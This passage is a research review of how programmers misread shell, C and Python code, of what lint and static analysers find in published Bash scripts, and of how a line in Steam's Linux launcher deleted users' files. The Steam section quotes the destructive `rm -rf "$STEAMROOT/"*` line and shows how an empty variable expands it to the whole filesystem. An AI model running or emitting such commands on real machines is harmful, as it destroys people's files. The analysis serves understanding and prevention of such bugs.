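Doane, Polson and Kintsch (1990), in *Design Issues for Graphical UNIX User Interfaces*, concluded that people need more than five years of experience to begin composing complex commands fluently. The group averages don't support such a precise figure, since the skill could develop at any point between two years and five. The experts may also have differed from the others in more than practice. The part of the study that followed people over time helps a little. Most participants improved, learning simple commands before complex ones, but expertise could also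 decline, depending on how people used the system.

The comprehension tasks would be more informative about reading, but the main finding and the group's later work are about producing commands. In *Cognitive Constraints on Computer Problem-Solving Skills*, for example, Sohn and Doane (1997) again asked people to produce complex commands and gave them hints when they made mistakes.

### What the less experienced users were missing

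In a second paper, *Action Planning*, Doane, McNamara and colleagues (1991) used hints of this kind to find out what people lacked. They gave 21 composite tasks to 22 computer science and electrical engineering students with between six months and six years of UNIX experience. The task and a list of the available files stayed on the screen. After each wrong answer, the experimenter handed the student a card naming the type of error, and the computer displayed another hint. The hints came in the same order whatever the mistake.

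One task was to format the text in the file `ATT2` and store the result in `ATT1`. The answer was `nroff -ms ATT2>ATT1`, where `nroff` is a text-formatting program. The hints for it were:

| Hint | What it told the student | Who benefited |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | a command that formats text is needed | not compared |
| 2 | that command is `nroff -ms` | novices and intermediates |
| 3 | a special symbol sends output to a file | experts |
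| 4 | that symbol is `>` | novices and intermediates |
| 5 | a reminder of both parts | experts |
| 6 | run `nroff -ms` on `ATT2`, then send its output to `ATT1` | novices and intermediates |
| 7 | the exact parts, not necessarily in order | not compared |
| 8 | the command comes first, followed by `>` | novices and intermediates |
| 9 | the complete answer | not compared |

Once experts knew they needed a symbol to send output to a file, they could usually supply it themselves. For the other students, a list of the right parts often wasn't enough, and they improved when a hint gave the order of those parts.

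These results come from only the first four tasks, where most of the learning took place, and the groups were small: the statistical tests imply ten novices, eight intermediates and four experts. The hints are also hard to compare because they came in a fixed order. By the time hint 6 appeared, a student had already made six attempts, and most experts had nothing left to learn from it. Doane, Sohn and colleagues (1994), in *Learning from Instruction*, looked more closely at six of the students on the tasks that required the most new knowledge. The two novices reached a perfect score only after the last hint, which gave the answer. Hint 4 didn't help the two intermediates, although it had helped intermediates in the fuller results.

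The researchers also counted an answer as correct only if it used the fewest possible keystrokes, because they wanted to make people use pipes. A student who typed `sort file1>temp; head temp>file2` instead of `sort file1|head>file2` got the right contents into `file2` but still received an error card. The cards distinguished long answers from ones that did the wrong thing, but the percentages of correct answers combine both kinds as errors, so they understate how many students could complete the task.

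### Why order might be the hard part

Doane and colleagues explain these results with UNICOM, a computer simulation of a person writing UNIX commands. The 1989 version contains 88 facts about UNIX and 11 plans. Each plan has a result, such as a sorted file, and conditions that must hold before the simulation can carry it out.

The simulation first works out which facts and plans are relevant to a task. If the task description contributes *m* facts, each starts with an activation of 1/*m*, and everything else starts at zero. The program repeatedly multiplies these values by a table of connection strengths, resetting the task's own facts to 1/*m* each time, until the values settle. It then tries the plans in order of activation and carries out the first one whose conditions hold. For `ls | sort | head`, this goes as follows:

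1. The plan for `head` is the most active, but it needs a sorted list of names, which doesn't exist yet. The plan for `sort` comes next, but it needs a list to sort. The plan for `ls` can go ahead, so the simulation records `ls` as the first command.
2. The simulation tries `head` again and still can't use it. `sort` now has a list to work on, so it becomes the second command.
3. `head` now has its sorted list and becomes the third.
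4. A separate plan joins the commands with pipes. It requires the syntax of each command, its place in the order, and whether it can pass data to or accept data from another command.

A user who works this way has to keep track of which commands are already in place, what each has produced and where that result should go. Doane and colleagues argue that this overloads the memory of less experienced users, and that experts' knowledge reduces the load.

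Two observations fit this account. Experts paused longer before typing a composite command than before typing a simpler one, as if they were planning it, while novices did not. In the 1991 study, the less experienced students left out or substituted many more symbols than the experts, and these mistakes became much less common after a hint gave the order. But the hint may have helped by supplying a fact the students didn't know, so the result doesn't establish that memory caused the mistakes. The simulation shows that the proposed steps are enough to produce the right command, but not that people follow them.

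### How much this says about reading

A finished command already shows the programs, symbols and order that the nine hints provided, so someone who could not have written `sort file1 | head > file2` may still understand it. Failure rates for writing commands are therefore probably higher than failure rates for reading them.

The reader still has to notice that, in this example, `head` receives the sorted lines, not the original `file1`, and that its output goes to `file2` instead of the screen. A reader can work from left to right, remembering only the latest result, whereas the simulated writer works backward from the goal to what it requires. If the memory account is right, reading a pipeline should be easier than writing one.

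Readers also need to know which programs accept input from a pipe, because the symbols don't show this. For example, `ls` ignores piped input, so `find . -name '*.log' | ls` lists the current directory, even though it looks like it would list the log files.

Reading shell code may be harder than writing it in one respect, because a reader has to understand whatever commands and operators someone else chose, while a writer can stick to familiar ones.

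The Doane studies give good evidence that people can learn about pipes in a course and still be unable to use them. They reveal little about how often people misread a pipeline, and their tasks involved combining programs, not quotes, word splitting or wildcards.

### Small patterns that mislead C programmers

In *Understanding misunderstandings in source code* (2017), Gopstein, Iannacone and colleagues tested directly how people read C. They looked for "atoms of confusion", the smallest pieces of code that cause people to predict the wrong output. One example is the number `013`, which looks like thirteen but equals eleven because C treats a number with a leading zero as base eight.

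One experiment compared 19 patterns suspected of confusing programmers with plainer code that did the same thing. It used 63 pairs of short programs, averaging four lines each. Each of the 73 participants worked through 84 of the 126 programs by hand and wrote down the output. For 15 of the 19 patterns, people made significantly more mistakes on the suspect version. A second experiment gave 43 people larger programs, and they again made more errors on the versions with the patterns.

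The paired design is the study's main strength. Both versions have the same output, so a difference in errors must come from the notation or from some side effect of rewriting it. The error rates don't carry over to ordinary code. The patterns came from entries to a contest for deliberately unreadable C programs, as Gopstein (2017) explains in *Atoms of Confusion*. The participants were students, according to *Atoms of Confusion in Java* (2021), which applied the idea to Java. Of the 14 patterns with a Java equivalent, seven led students to make significantly more mistakes.

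In *Thinking Aloud about Confusing Code*, Gopstein, Fayard and colleagues (2020) asked 14 people to explain their reasoning as they read eight short programs, six with a suspected confusing pattern and two without. The participants were five master's students, four professional C++ developers, and five professionals who wrote a widely used C++ library. Nobody made a mistake on the plain programs. On the others, the students gave 14 wrong answers out of 30 (47%), and the professionals gave 3 out of 54 (6%). The sample is tiny, and all the professionals worked at one company.

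Three of the 17 mistakes involved this line:

```
if (++V1 || ++V2) ...
```

Here `++` adds one to a variable, and `||` means "or". C evaluates the right side only if the left side is false, so `V2` doesn't change when the left side is true. One student thought that both variables would always increase. A professional with 39 years of programming experience knew that C could skip the right side but thought it did so when the left side was false. The paper's explanation of the line makes the same mistake, stating that C evaluates the right side only if the left is true. The shell's `||` also skips the command after it if the one before it succeeds, so this is some of the closest experimental evidence on reading chained commands.

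The interviews also showed that the mistakes had different causes. Some people had never seen the notation, while others recognised it but had learned the wrong rule. In two cases, Gopstein and colleagues attributed the error to knowledge of another language. One student assumed that C ignores a leading zero because they wrongly believed that Python does. A C programmer who groups a shell chain by C's precedence rules makes the same kind of mistake.

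A few errors were lapses of attention. The professional who misremembered the rule for `||` also gave the output as "one, two" instead of "two, one", after correctly working out that `V1` was 2 and `V2` was 1. The researchers suspected that the digits in the variable names had interfered. The person was going through the code aloud, step by step, so this differs from approving a command without reading it.

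### When experience helps and when it hurts

The gap between students and professionals suggests that experience reduces misreading. The benefit was less consistent in a larger Python experiment, reported in *What Makes Code Hard to Understand?* (2013). Hansen, Goldstone and Lumsdaine asked 162 people to predict the exact output of ten short programs. Each program had two or three slightly different versions, and participants saw one randomly chosen version of each. They averaged two years of experience with Python and nearly seven with programming in general, but 94 had used Python for a year or less.

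Participants gave exactly the right output in 1,007 of 1,602 attempts, or 63%. Some of the other answers were wrong only in their formatting, so participants misunderstood the code in fewer than 37% of attempts. Python experience helped modestly, with each extra year adding about 1.2 points to a total score out of 100.

On one program, however, experience made a particular mistake more likely. The program took two lists of numbers, selected the values within a certain range from each, and printed the results. It then printed the numbers that the two original lists had in common:

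| | First list | Second list | Numbers in common |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original | 2, 8, 7, 9, -5, 0, 2 | 1, -3, 10, 0, 8, 9, 1 | 8, 9, 0 |
| After selection | 8, 7, 9 | 1, 0, 8, 1 | 8 |

The correct last line was `[8, 9, 0]`, but 22% of participants answered `[8]`, the result of comparing the shortened lists. One participant later said this had seemed the logical next step. The odds of this mistake were about 1.4 times as high for each additional year of Python experience. The text gives p < 0.5 for this effect, which must be a misprint for 0.05, since the paper's results table marks it as significant.

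Hansen and colleagues suggest that experienced programmers expect each step to use the result of the previous one. That expectation is usually right and makes reading faster, but here it led people to see a connection that wasn't in the code. Someone reading shell code could make a similar mistake with `sort names.txt > sorted.txt; head names.txt`, where the second command reads the original unsorted file.

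In another program, `+` added numbers twice and then joined the texts `"5"` and `"3"` into `53`. More experienced programmers slowed down more than others when the meaning of `+` changed, though they weren't significantly less accurate. When functions were defined in an unexpected order, experience instead reduced the delay, because programmers often see functions out of order in real code and are used to reading them.

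Misleading names caused errors at every level of experience. One program called functions named `add_1` and `twice` on a variable that held 4. Neither function returned a value, so the variable stayed at 4, but around half of the participants got this wrong. Many answered 22, the value the names implied. Participants with more Python experience were less likely to give that answer.

Layout had one of the largest effects. In Python, indentation determines which lines belong to a loop, and blank lines have no effect. One version of a program put two blank lines before the last line of its loop:

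```
for i in [1, 2, 3, 4]:
    print "The count is", i

    print "Done counting"
```

The code prints "Done counting" four times. With the blank lines, 59% of participants thought it would print this only once, at the end, compared with 15% without them. Experience made no significant difference. Participants apparently used the blank lines to decide which lines belonged together, even though the indentation determines this.

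Spacing affected arithmetic too. Participants presumably all knew from school to multiply before adding, but they were more likely to add first when a set of similar formulas wasn't lined up in columns. This suggests that a reader can know an operator's precedence and still group an expression by how it looks. A one-liner has few such visual cues, and extra space around `&&` or `||` doesn't change how the shell groups the commands.

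### Are pipelines and dense lines actually harder?

There is little evidence that a line is hard to read just because it does a lot. Hansen and colleagues tested a similar idea with three versions of a program that used a function `f`, which adds 4 to a number. The first version multiplied the results of three calls on a single line, as `f(1)*f(0)*f(-1)`. The second added spaces around the operators, and the third stored each result in its own variable before multiplying.

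| Version | Lines in the program | Average mark out of 10 | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| One line, no spaces | 4 | 9.1 | 38.6 seconds |
| One line, with spaces | 4 | 8.8 | 35.9 seconds |
| A variable for each result | 7 | 9.8 | 36.9 seconds |

The version with separate variables had the highest average, but the differences in marks weren't statistically significant, and the times were almost the same. The task was easy, and a real difference can go undetected when nearly everyone gets full marks. The three calls were also independent of each other, while in a pipeline each program works on the previous one's output.

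Two of the other programs are also evidence against a simple link between length and difficulty. In one, which calculated the areas of two rectangles, the shortest version (14 lines) took the longest to read because it stored the coordinates in pairs and used awkward notation to extract them. The longest version (21 lines) was no slower to read than the basic one. In the program with the two lists, moving repeated code into named functions didn't improve answers. The average mark was 4.7 with functions and 5.8 with the code written out twice.

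*Using a Command Language as a High-Level Programming Language*, an early paper on the UNIX shell, calls the pipe "especially desirable, both for human comprehension and for computer performance". This is an opinion without an experiment behind it, but it is worth taking seriously because a pipeline lists the steps in the order the data passes through them. It also needs no names for intermediate results, so the reader doesn't have to check whether a later command uses `temp1` or `temp2`.

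The Doane studies don't test this view, although composite commands caused a lot of trouble in them. They compared pipelines with sets of unrelated commands, which were easier because no step depended on another. A fair comparison would set `sort file1 | head > file2` against the same job done with a temporary file. The 1991 study counted the second form as an error, so its results can't show which form people find easier. The difficulty might come from the dependence between steps, which both forms share, rather than from the pipe.

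Breaking up a one-liner can help the reader if it removes a confusing operator or gives a value a useful name. But these experiments give no strong reason to expect fewer mistakes if it only spreads the same steps over more lines.

### What a prediction test can miss

Most of these reading experiments judged understanding by whether people predicted the right output. Interviews by Gopstein and colleagues showed that this measure can mislead in both directions. One program contained the condition `0 && 1 || 2`, intended to test whether people knew that `&&` has higher precedence than `||` in C. Two students got it wrong, but neither had trouble with precedence. One thought 2 couldn't count as true, and the other thought a condition had to contain a variable.

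Some people who didn't know the precedence rule still answered correctly. One of the library authors believed that `&&` and `||` had equal precedence and that C evaluated them from left to right. This gives the right result for `0 && 1 || 2`, but would give the wrong one for `2 || 1 && 0`. The same belief would be correct in Bash, which does group the two operators this way.

In a study by Gopstein and colleagues, only 10 of the 17 wrong answers came solely from the pattern the program was supposed to test. They concluded that right-or-wrong tests may underestimate misunderstanding, because a lucky answer counts as a success. Such tests may also lead researchers to attribute an error to the wrong feature. A trial on shell commands would also underestimate misunderstanding if it used only lines where the mistaken and correct readings give the same result.

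The test conditions can also help people. Gopstein and colleagues told participants that every program ran without errors, and some participants used this to rule out their first interpretation. People reading a command from a colleague or an AI agent don't have that guarantee. The test also added some difficulty, because several professionals rarely used `printf`, the function that displayed the output, and were unsure about it.

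A bigger difference from everyday shell use is that the C and Python programs contained nearly everything a reader needed. Readers could see or work out the variables' values, and the Doane studies kept the list of files on the screen. The experiments are therefore useful for studying misparses, because missing information about variables or files can't explain the errors. However, they don't cover cases where someone reads `rm -r $dir` correctly but has no way of knowing what `dir` contains.

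Predicting a command's exact output is also a stricter test than deciding whether it is safe. Someone may be wrong about which ten lines `head` will print and still see that the command only reads a file. A person may also describe the purpose of a cleanup command correctly but miss the operator that makes it delete the wrong directory. Error rates from these experiments therefore don't show how often people approve harmful commands. To measure that, researchers have to ask people whether they would approve a command.

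## How common are these mistakes in published scripts, and what do lint tools catch?

The experiments above tested how people read C and Python and how they write UNIX commands, but not how they read Bash. A program can search millions of published scripts for missing quotes, unchecked `cd` commands and other mistakes. These searches cover real work and far more code than an experiment could, but they show only what people wrote, not what they expected it to do.

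Most of the figures come from ShellCheck, the lint tool that warns about `A && B || C`. A lint tool looks for code smells, patterns that the tool's developers consider risky even if the code never fails.

### How ShellCheck finds a smell

ShellCheck parses a script and compares its commands, words and expansions with a list of patterns. Each match produces a report with a line number, a severity (error, warning, info or style), a code and a short message. Dong, Li and colleagues (2022), in *Bash in the Wild*, give this example:

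```
x="this is a sentence"
if [ $x = "..." ]; then
```

The shell splits the value of `x` into four words, so `[` receives too many arguments and fails with an error. ShellCheck reports the missing quotes as SC2086, with the message "Double quote to prevent globbing and word splitting."

When a variable's value comes from a user, a file or another program, as it often does, ShellCheck can't determine whether it will contain a space. It also can't determine what the programmer intended. *ABASH* gives the example `mv $FILES "$DIR"`, where `FILES` holds several file names separated by spaces. The command works only because the shell splits `FILES`, so quoting that variable would break it. ShellCheck is designed on the assumption that programmers normally want quotes, so it flags deliberate as well as accidental splitting.

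### More than a million scripts

Dong and colleagues collected 1,352,768 different Bash scripts from 516,659 public GitHub repositories, and another 14,387 scripts from the 1,000 shell projects with the most stars. They ran ShellCheck on the latest version of each script and counted every report except those about style.

ShellCheck reported at least one problem in 80.9% of the general scripts and 53.5% of those from popular projects. The paper lists the five most common codes in each group:

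| Code | What it warns about | General scripts | Popular projects |
|---|---|---|---|
| SC2164 | `cd` with nothing to handle a failure | 21.5% | 8.1% |
| SC2046 | unquoted `$(...)`, whose output the shell splits | 20.9% | 9.5% |
| SC2162 | `read` without `-r`, which removes backslashes from the input | 12% | not in the top five |
| SC2155 | `export x=$(cmd)` and similar lines, which hide a failure of `cmd` | 8.7% | 5.3% |
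| SC2068 | an unquoted list of values, such as `$@` | 6% | 2.6% |
| SC2128 | `$list` for an array, which gives only its first value | not in the top five | 3.2% |

The most common warning, SC2164, flags a `cd` command with no check for failure. In `cd /foo; rm -f *`, the shell deletes files in the wrong directory if `cd` fails. ShellCheck also gives this warning when no `rm` follows, so many of these scripts would only have printed some errors or written a file to the wrong directory if `cd` had failed.

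The general figure may be too high for GitHub as a whole. GitHub's search returned at most 1,000 files per query, so the researchers split the search into 25,000 queries by file size, up to 50,000 bytes. When a size was very common, they got only some of the files of that size. The sample therefore probably has a higher share of large scripts than GitHub does, and larger scripts tend to produce more reports. The table of severities also covers about 28,500 fewer scripts than the researchers collected, and they don't explain why.

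The correlation between a script's size and its number of reports was 0.38, which Dong and colleagues call moderately positive, so size accounts for about 14% of the variation. Longer scripts have more lines for ShellCheck to flag, so this doesn't show that people write them less carefully. Testing that would require the number of reports per line.

Dong and colleagues suggest that popular projects have fewer reports because they have more maintainers and more review, and because some of them run lint tools before publishing. This is plausible. Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues report in *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects* that more than 60% of popular shell repositories on GitHub now use ShellCheck.

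But scripts in popular projects are also less likely to use commands that can go wrong. Only 20.2% of them use `cd`, compared with 38.1% of the general scripts, and 17.7% use `rm`, compared with 33.1%. If nearly all SC2164 reports concern `cd`, then ShellCheck flagged about 56% of the general scripts that use it and about 40% of the popular ones. The relative difference is much smaller than when counting all scripts in each group, where the figures are 21.5% and 8.1%.

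Of the general scripts, 13.7% use `read`, which reads a line of input into a variable, and 12% have a report for leaving out `-r`. By the same calculation, nearly nine in ten scripts that use `read` have this smell. It matters only if the input contains a backslash, as in `C:\new`, which `read` would store as `C:new`. A script that asks the user to type "yes" or "no" may never have a problem.

### The missing warning about unquoted variables

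Neither list includes SC2086, the basic warning about an unquoted variable. This is odd, because unquoted variables are a standard example of a shell mistake, and Dong and colleagues use an SC2086 report as their example of ShellCheck's output. That report has the severity "info", a level they included in their counts.

The paper is based on a master's thesis, *An Empirical Study on Bash Language Usage in Github* (Li, 2021), which has the same lists. The thesis gives the ShellCheck version (0.7.0) and the exact command, which doesn't turn off any warnings, but it doesn't explain the absence either.

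The published figures seem incomplete. ShellCheck flagged 53.5% of scripts in the popular projects, but the five listed codes can account for at most 28.7%, the sum of their shares. At least 24.8% of scripts must therefore have had reports only for other codes. If the list is right, none of those other codes appeared in more than 2.6% of scripts, so at least ten would be needed to make up the difference. That is possible, since ShellCheck has many codes, but a simpler explanation would be that one very common code was left out of the count.

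The 20.9% for SC2046 is therefore best treated as a minimum for missing quotes in the general scripts, because it covers only unquoted command expansions. The share with an unquoted variable could be much higher.

### Which bugs people fixed

Dong and colleagues also looked for mistakes that programmers had corrected. They searched the descriptions of changes for words like "bug" and "fix", then randomly sampled 200 changes, half from five large, long-running projects and half from the general scripts. Three of the researchers examined each change separately, then settled any disagreements.

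Some changes fixed more than one thing, so the total was 214. Of these, 32 turned out not to be bug fixes or to concern code in another language, which leaves 182 real bugs:

| Cause | Bugs | Could ShellCheck catch them? |
|---|---|---|
| Quoting | 9 | most unquoted expansions, but few mix-ups between single and double quotes |
| Files and directories | 8 | no, since most scripts wrongly assumed that something existed |
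| Command options | 6 | very few |
| Permissions | 6 | no |
| Error handling | 6 | some, such as an unchecked `cd` |
| Other misuse of Bash or its commands | 22 | not broken down |
| Application logic | 122 | not assessed as a group |
| Syntax | 3 | not assessed as a group |

Quoting caused about 5% of the real bugs. With a sample this size, the true share could easily be from 3% to 9%. Li's earlier count has slightly different totals, with 127 bugs in application logic and two in syntax, but its share for quoting is almost the same.

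ShellCheck is weak on quote mix-ups because both forms can be correct, and the line alone doesn't show which one the programmer intended. Dong and colleagues point out that a lint tool could detect invalid options by looking them up in the manual, but it would still miss a valid option that does the wrong job.

If ShellCheck can't detect errors in application logic either, it could have caught at most 46 of the 182 bugs, or 25%. That is a generous estimate because it assumes ShellCheck would find every syntax error and every misuse of Bash except those involving missing files and permissions.

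**Lint reports and fixed bugs.** At least a fifth of the general scripts have a missing quote, but quoting accounts for only about a twentieth of the bugs people fixed. These percentages measure different things, so their ratio is not the chance that a missing quote causes a failure. Still, the contrast suggests that most missing quotes never cause a failure that anyone notices. Programmers usually run their scripts on their own files, and many avoid spaces in file names.

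The count of fixed bugs also leaves out quoting mistakes that nobody noticed, such as one that made a backup skip every file with a space in its name. The search would have missed a change described as "add quotes", because that phrase contains none of the search terms.

### How ShellCheck does on known failures

Lazarek and colleagues collected 61 programs containing 116 documented bugs, along with a corrected version of each program. The sources included GitHub, Stack Overflow and Debian's bug tracker. They ran ShellCheck 0.11.0 with its optional checks turned on, and counted a bug as caught if any warning was related to it, even if the message didn't describe the actual problem.

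ShellCheck found 42 of the 116 bugs, or 36%. Of those, 18 came from one database backup script whose author wrote comments with `//`, as in C, instead of `#`. In a line such as `HOST=db1 // main server`, the shell tries to run `//` as a command and sets `HOST` only for that command, so the value isn't available to later lines. Excluding this script, ShellCheck found 24 of 98 bugs, or 24%.

In seven of the 42 cases, ShellCheck still gave the same warning after the bug was gone. This is a weakness of pattern matching. A script may check that a variable isn't empty before using it in an `rm` command, but a rule that looks only at the `rm` will flag the line anyway.

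The researchers then rewrote the programs ShellCheck had flagged, keeping all 42 bugs but changing the wording. ShellCheck found none of them. In the backup script, for example, they stored `//` in a variable called `c` and wrote `$c` wherever `//` had been. No one would normally write this, so the result shows that small changes can hide a bug from ShellCheck, but not how often that happens in ordinary scripts.

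### Tools that work out what a script would do

Some analysers try to predict a script's behaviour instead of matching patterns. ABASH, which Mazurak and Zdancewic built in 2007, checks whether each argument could expand to no words, one word or several. It then uses heuristics to identify which splits are probably accidental. One heuristic is that a word made of several parts, such as `$FOO/$BAR`, is almost certainly meant to remain a single word.

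Mazurak and Zdancewic tried ABASH on 49 scripts from two software download sites and 60 startup scripts from Ubuntu, a version of Linux:

| | Downloaded scripts (49) | Ubuntu startup scripts (60) |
|---|---|---|
| Scripts with an expansion bug | 20 | 0 |
| Scripts with a false warning | 11 | 11 |
| Scripts where an argument could turn into an option | 39 | 31 |

In 13 of the 20 faulty scripts, a user could trigger the problem through their input or their own files. One script for managing disk images ran `rm -rf` on a path that included an unquoted argument. If an administrator let other people run that script as root, they could delete any file on the system by putting a space in the argument.

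ABASH counts a script as having a bug if some value could make it misbehave. Dong and colleagues counted only problems that someone had fixed, so ABASH's 41% for downloaded scripts is more comparable to a lint figure than to their 5%. The ABASH sample is small and old. It suggests that heavily used scripts contain fewer expansion mistakes, but the Ubuntu scripts were also shorter and simpler.

The last row of the table covers the problem with `rm *` and a file called `-r`. Only two of the downloaded scripts used `-` or `--` to mark the end of the options. ABASH produced so many warnings of this kind that Mazurak and Zdancewic found them tedious to use, and most of the warnings probably didn't point to an exploitable bug.

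Narsipur's *Statically Analyzing Shell Scripts and Their Effects in Context* describes Shseer, an analyser that tracks what a script does to files. It uses symbolic execution, which means stepping through a program with placeholders for unknown values. When a command could succeed or fail, Shseer follows both possibilities and records what must be true in each.

Shseer also needs a specification of what each command requires and what it changes. In `rm a.txt; cat a.txt`, the specifications conflict because `rm` deletes `a.txt` and `cat` needs the file to exist in order to print it. Shseer can therefore report a bug even though neither command looks suspicious by itself.

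Shseer assumes that an unknown variable always stands for one argument and never for an option, which keeps the number of possibilities manageable. The same assumption misleads people reading `cp $file $target`, so Shseer can't detect mistakes that depend on it.

SaSh, a later analyser by Lazarek, Narsipur and others, allows for an unknown variable expanding into several arguments, but still assumes that none of them is an option. For each unknown value, it records any fixed text at the start or end and the number of words the value could become. In `rm $1/usr`, it can detect that `rm` will receive `/usr` as a separate argument if `$1` ends with a space. It also records whether anything has read a file since the script wrote it, so it can flag `mv a x.txt; mv b x.txt`, where the second command overwrites the file the first just moved.

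SaSh found 115 of the 116 documented bugs and all 42 of the reworded ones, and it stopped warning about each bug once the script was fixed. It found 97 of the 116 within a second. It would probably do less well on other programs, because the researchers chose the kinds of bug it looks for after studying the same programs it was tested on.

In a better test, the researchers ran SaSh on open-source projects with no known bugs. It found 70 bugs in 44 projects, including the machine-learning library PyTorch and Kubernetes, a system for running software across many computers. The researchers checked each bug by hand and reported it, and maintainers had accepted 27 fixes by the time of writing. But the paper doesn't report how many warnings they had to read to find those 70 bugs, which would matter a lot to anyone using the tool every day.

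The one documented bug that SaSh missed was in a script for installing Debian, another version of Linux. When a user asked for a list of required packages, the script printed the list and then deleted the directory the user had named. Deleting a directory that the user names is often legitimate, so SaSh doesn't treat it as a mistake. Catching this bug requires knowing that a script shouldn't delete the user's files when asked only for a list.

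Writing a specification for every shell command by hand takes a long time. *Caruca* (Lamprou, Lazarek and colleagues, 2025) automates the work. It uses a language model to turn a command's manual into a list of its options. It then runs the command in an isolated copy of the file system, with many combinations of options and files, and records what changes. For `rm` alone, it generates more than 8.7 million combinations.

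Caruca supplies the specifications for Shseer. It produced correct specifications for 59 of the 60 commands that already had handwritten ones, but it can miss behaviour that depends on environment variables (settings that a program receives from the shell) because it doesn't vary them.

Lamprou and colleagues counted the options in about 665,000 commands from 49,000 scripts on GitHub to decide which combinations of options to try. About 65% of the commands had no options and another 29% had just one. Readers of shell code therefore seldom see many options in one command, though a single option like `-r` can change what a command deletes.

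*Analysing installation scenarios of Debian packages*, from the CoLiS research project, applied symbolic execution to the scripts that Debian runs when someone installs, updates or removes a package. Nearly all of the 28,814 scripts are written in POSIX shell, and they run with full administrator rights. The paper reported more than 150 violations of Debian's own rules, and maintainers had fixed over half of them by the time it appeared. This low count isn't a bug rate, because the tool checked only certain rules and could not analyse every script.

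### A smell, a bug and a misreading

A line can contain a smell without having a bug, and either can occur without anyone misreading the line, so the 80.9% does not measure how badly programmers understand the shell.

The line `tmp=$(mktemp); rm $tmp` creates a temporary file and then deletes it. ShellCheck warns about the unquoted variable, but `mktemp` normally chooses a name without spaces, so the line works, and a reader who takes `rm $tmp` to mean "delete the temporary file" is right.

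A script can also fail even though its author understood every line. Eight of the bugs that Dong and colleagues examined involved files or directories, usually ones the programmer had assumed would exist, and six involved permissions. These are mostly cases of missing state. Many of the SC2164 reports may be too, since someone who writes `cd build` without a check may know that `cd` can fail but expect the directory to be there.

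Lint rules are meant to help programmers avoid fragile code, so they can miss lines that are robust but easy to misread. ShellCheck's warning about mixed operators covers `A && B || C` but not `test -d build || mkdir build && rm -rf build/*`, which has the operators in the opposite order. C programmers can easily misread that line.

Dong and colleagues seem to misread Bash's double brackets in their paper. To illustrate a bug in application logic, they change `[[ cmd1 && cmd2 && cmd3 ]]` to `[[ cmd1 || cmd2 || cmd3 ]]`. If `cmd1` and the others are commands, as their names suggest, neither version runs them. The double brackets here only check that each piece of text isn't empty, so both tests always succeed. The names may just be placeholders for conditions, but if not, six authors studying Bash errors and the paper's reviewers missed the mistake.

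A flagged line in a published script is weaker evidence than this, because the author hasn't stated what they meant. They may have misparsed the line because they didn't know the rule. They may also have known the rule and judged the line safe, or copied the line without looking at it closely. ShellCheck would report the same thing in each case, and none of these studies asked the script authors.

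Researchers could find out with fairly little effort by giving programmers flagged lines from the GitHub collection, along with the variable values and file names, and asking what arguments each command would receive. Wrong answers would mean the programmers had misparsed the line, since they would have all the facts they needed.

The figures also come from scripts, which differ from a command that someone types or approves once. A script may run thousands of times on computers its author has never seen, so an unquoted variable is more likely to hold a file name with a space in it at some point than the same variable in a one-liner that runs once. But the author can test a script on unimportant files and correct it before anyone else uses it, while the first run of a one-liner may be on the files that matter.

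## How did one line of Steam's script delete users' files?

On Linux, a Bash script called `steam.sh` starts Steam, a program for buying and running games. On 14 January 2015, a user called keyvin reported that Steam had deleted almost every file that keyvin's account owned. keyvin had moved the Steam folder to another drive and left behind a symbolic link, a small file pointing to the new location. According to the report, which Virtual Curiosities' *It Happened* reproduces, Steam then failed to start, even after keyvin pointed it to the new folder. It crashed, then reinstalled itself at the next start and seemed to work. By then the files were gone, including those on a three-terabyte external drive that held the backups. Most of the important ones were also in online storage.

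Another user, doofy, lost files after starting `steam.sh` directly to debug it. According to Hackaday's *How A Steam Bug Once Deleted All Of Someone's User Data* (2024), doofy was the first to point out the command responsible:

```
rm -rf "$STEAMROOT/"*
```

`STEAMROOT` was supposed to hold the path of the Steam folder. If the variable is empty, this line deletes everything on the computer that the user has permission to delete.

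The copy of the script that people shared at the time was from 2013 and came from a third party's repository, as commenters noted in The Daily WTF's *Don't try to move Steam on \*NIX*. Huynh's *bash coding style*, a guide with a collection of shell accidents, preserves that copy. A patch that rcxdude (2015) wrote two days after keyvin's report shows parts of the 2015 version.

### From an empty variable to every directory

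The script sets the variable near the top:

```
STEAMROOT="$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"
```

`$0` holds the name used to start the script. `${0%/*}` removes the last slash and everything after it, which normally leaves the script's directory. The shell changes to that directory and prints `$PWD`, the full path of the current directory. The script stores this output in `STEAMROOT`.

Huynh explains that this fails if someone starts the script with `bash steam.sh`:

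| | Started by its full path | Started as `bash steam.sh` |
|---|---|---|
| `$0` | `/home/ana/Steam/steam.sh` | `steam.sh` |
| `${0%/*}` | `/home/ana/Steam` | `steam.sh` |
| `cd` | succeeds | fails, because `steam.sh` isn't a directory |
| `STEAMROOT` | `/home/ana/Steam` | empty |
| `"$STEAMROOT/"*` before globbing | `/home/ana/Steam/*` | `/*` |
| What `rm` receives | the files and folders in the Steam folder | `/bin`, `/etc`, `/home`, `/media`, `/usr` and so on |

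When `cd` fails, the `&&` keeps `echo` from running, so `$(...)` produces no text and `STEAMROOT` is empty. Virtual Curiosities explains this step differently, stating that `${0%/*}` is empty if `$0` has no slash, but the shell leaves the value unchanged in that case.

An ordinary user can't delete most of the operating system, but the command can still delete every file the user owns on any connected drive, as bit-tech's *Steam for Linux hit by file-deletion bug* pointed out. keyvin's backup drive was under `/media`, so the command could reach it.

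Quoting every variable would not have prevented the deletion. `$STEAMROOT` was already quoted, and `$PWD`, the only unquoted variable in the two lines, had nothing to do with it. Quotes keep a folder name with a space in one piece, but they don't replace a missing value. `$STEAMROOT/*`, `"$STEAMROOT"/*` and `"$STEAMROOT/"*` all become `/*` when the variable is empty, because the asterisk has to stay outside the quotes to work as a wildcard.

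Huynh's explanation fits doofy's case, since people often debug a script by running `bash -x steam.sh`, which prints each command. It doesn't explain keyvin's, because `cd` follows symbolic links, so a working link to the new folder wouldn't leave the variable empty. The report puts the original folder in `~/.local/share` but the link in `~/.local`, which may be a typo or may mean the link was in the wrong place. Valve, the company behind Steam, couldn't reproduce the bug, according to PC Gamer's *Valve investigating scary sounding Steam bug on Linux*. TechRaptor's *Major bug discovered steam linux* reports that its writer reproduced it on Fedora 21, another version of Linux.

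### How a failed start led to a deletion

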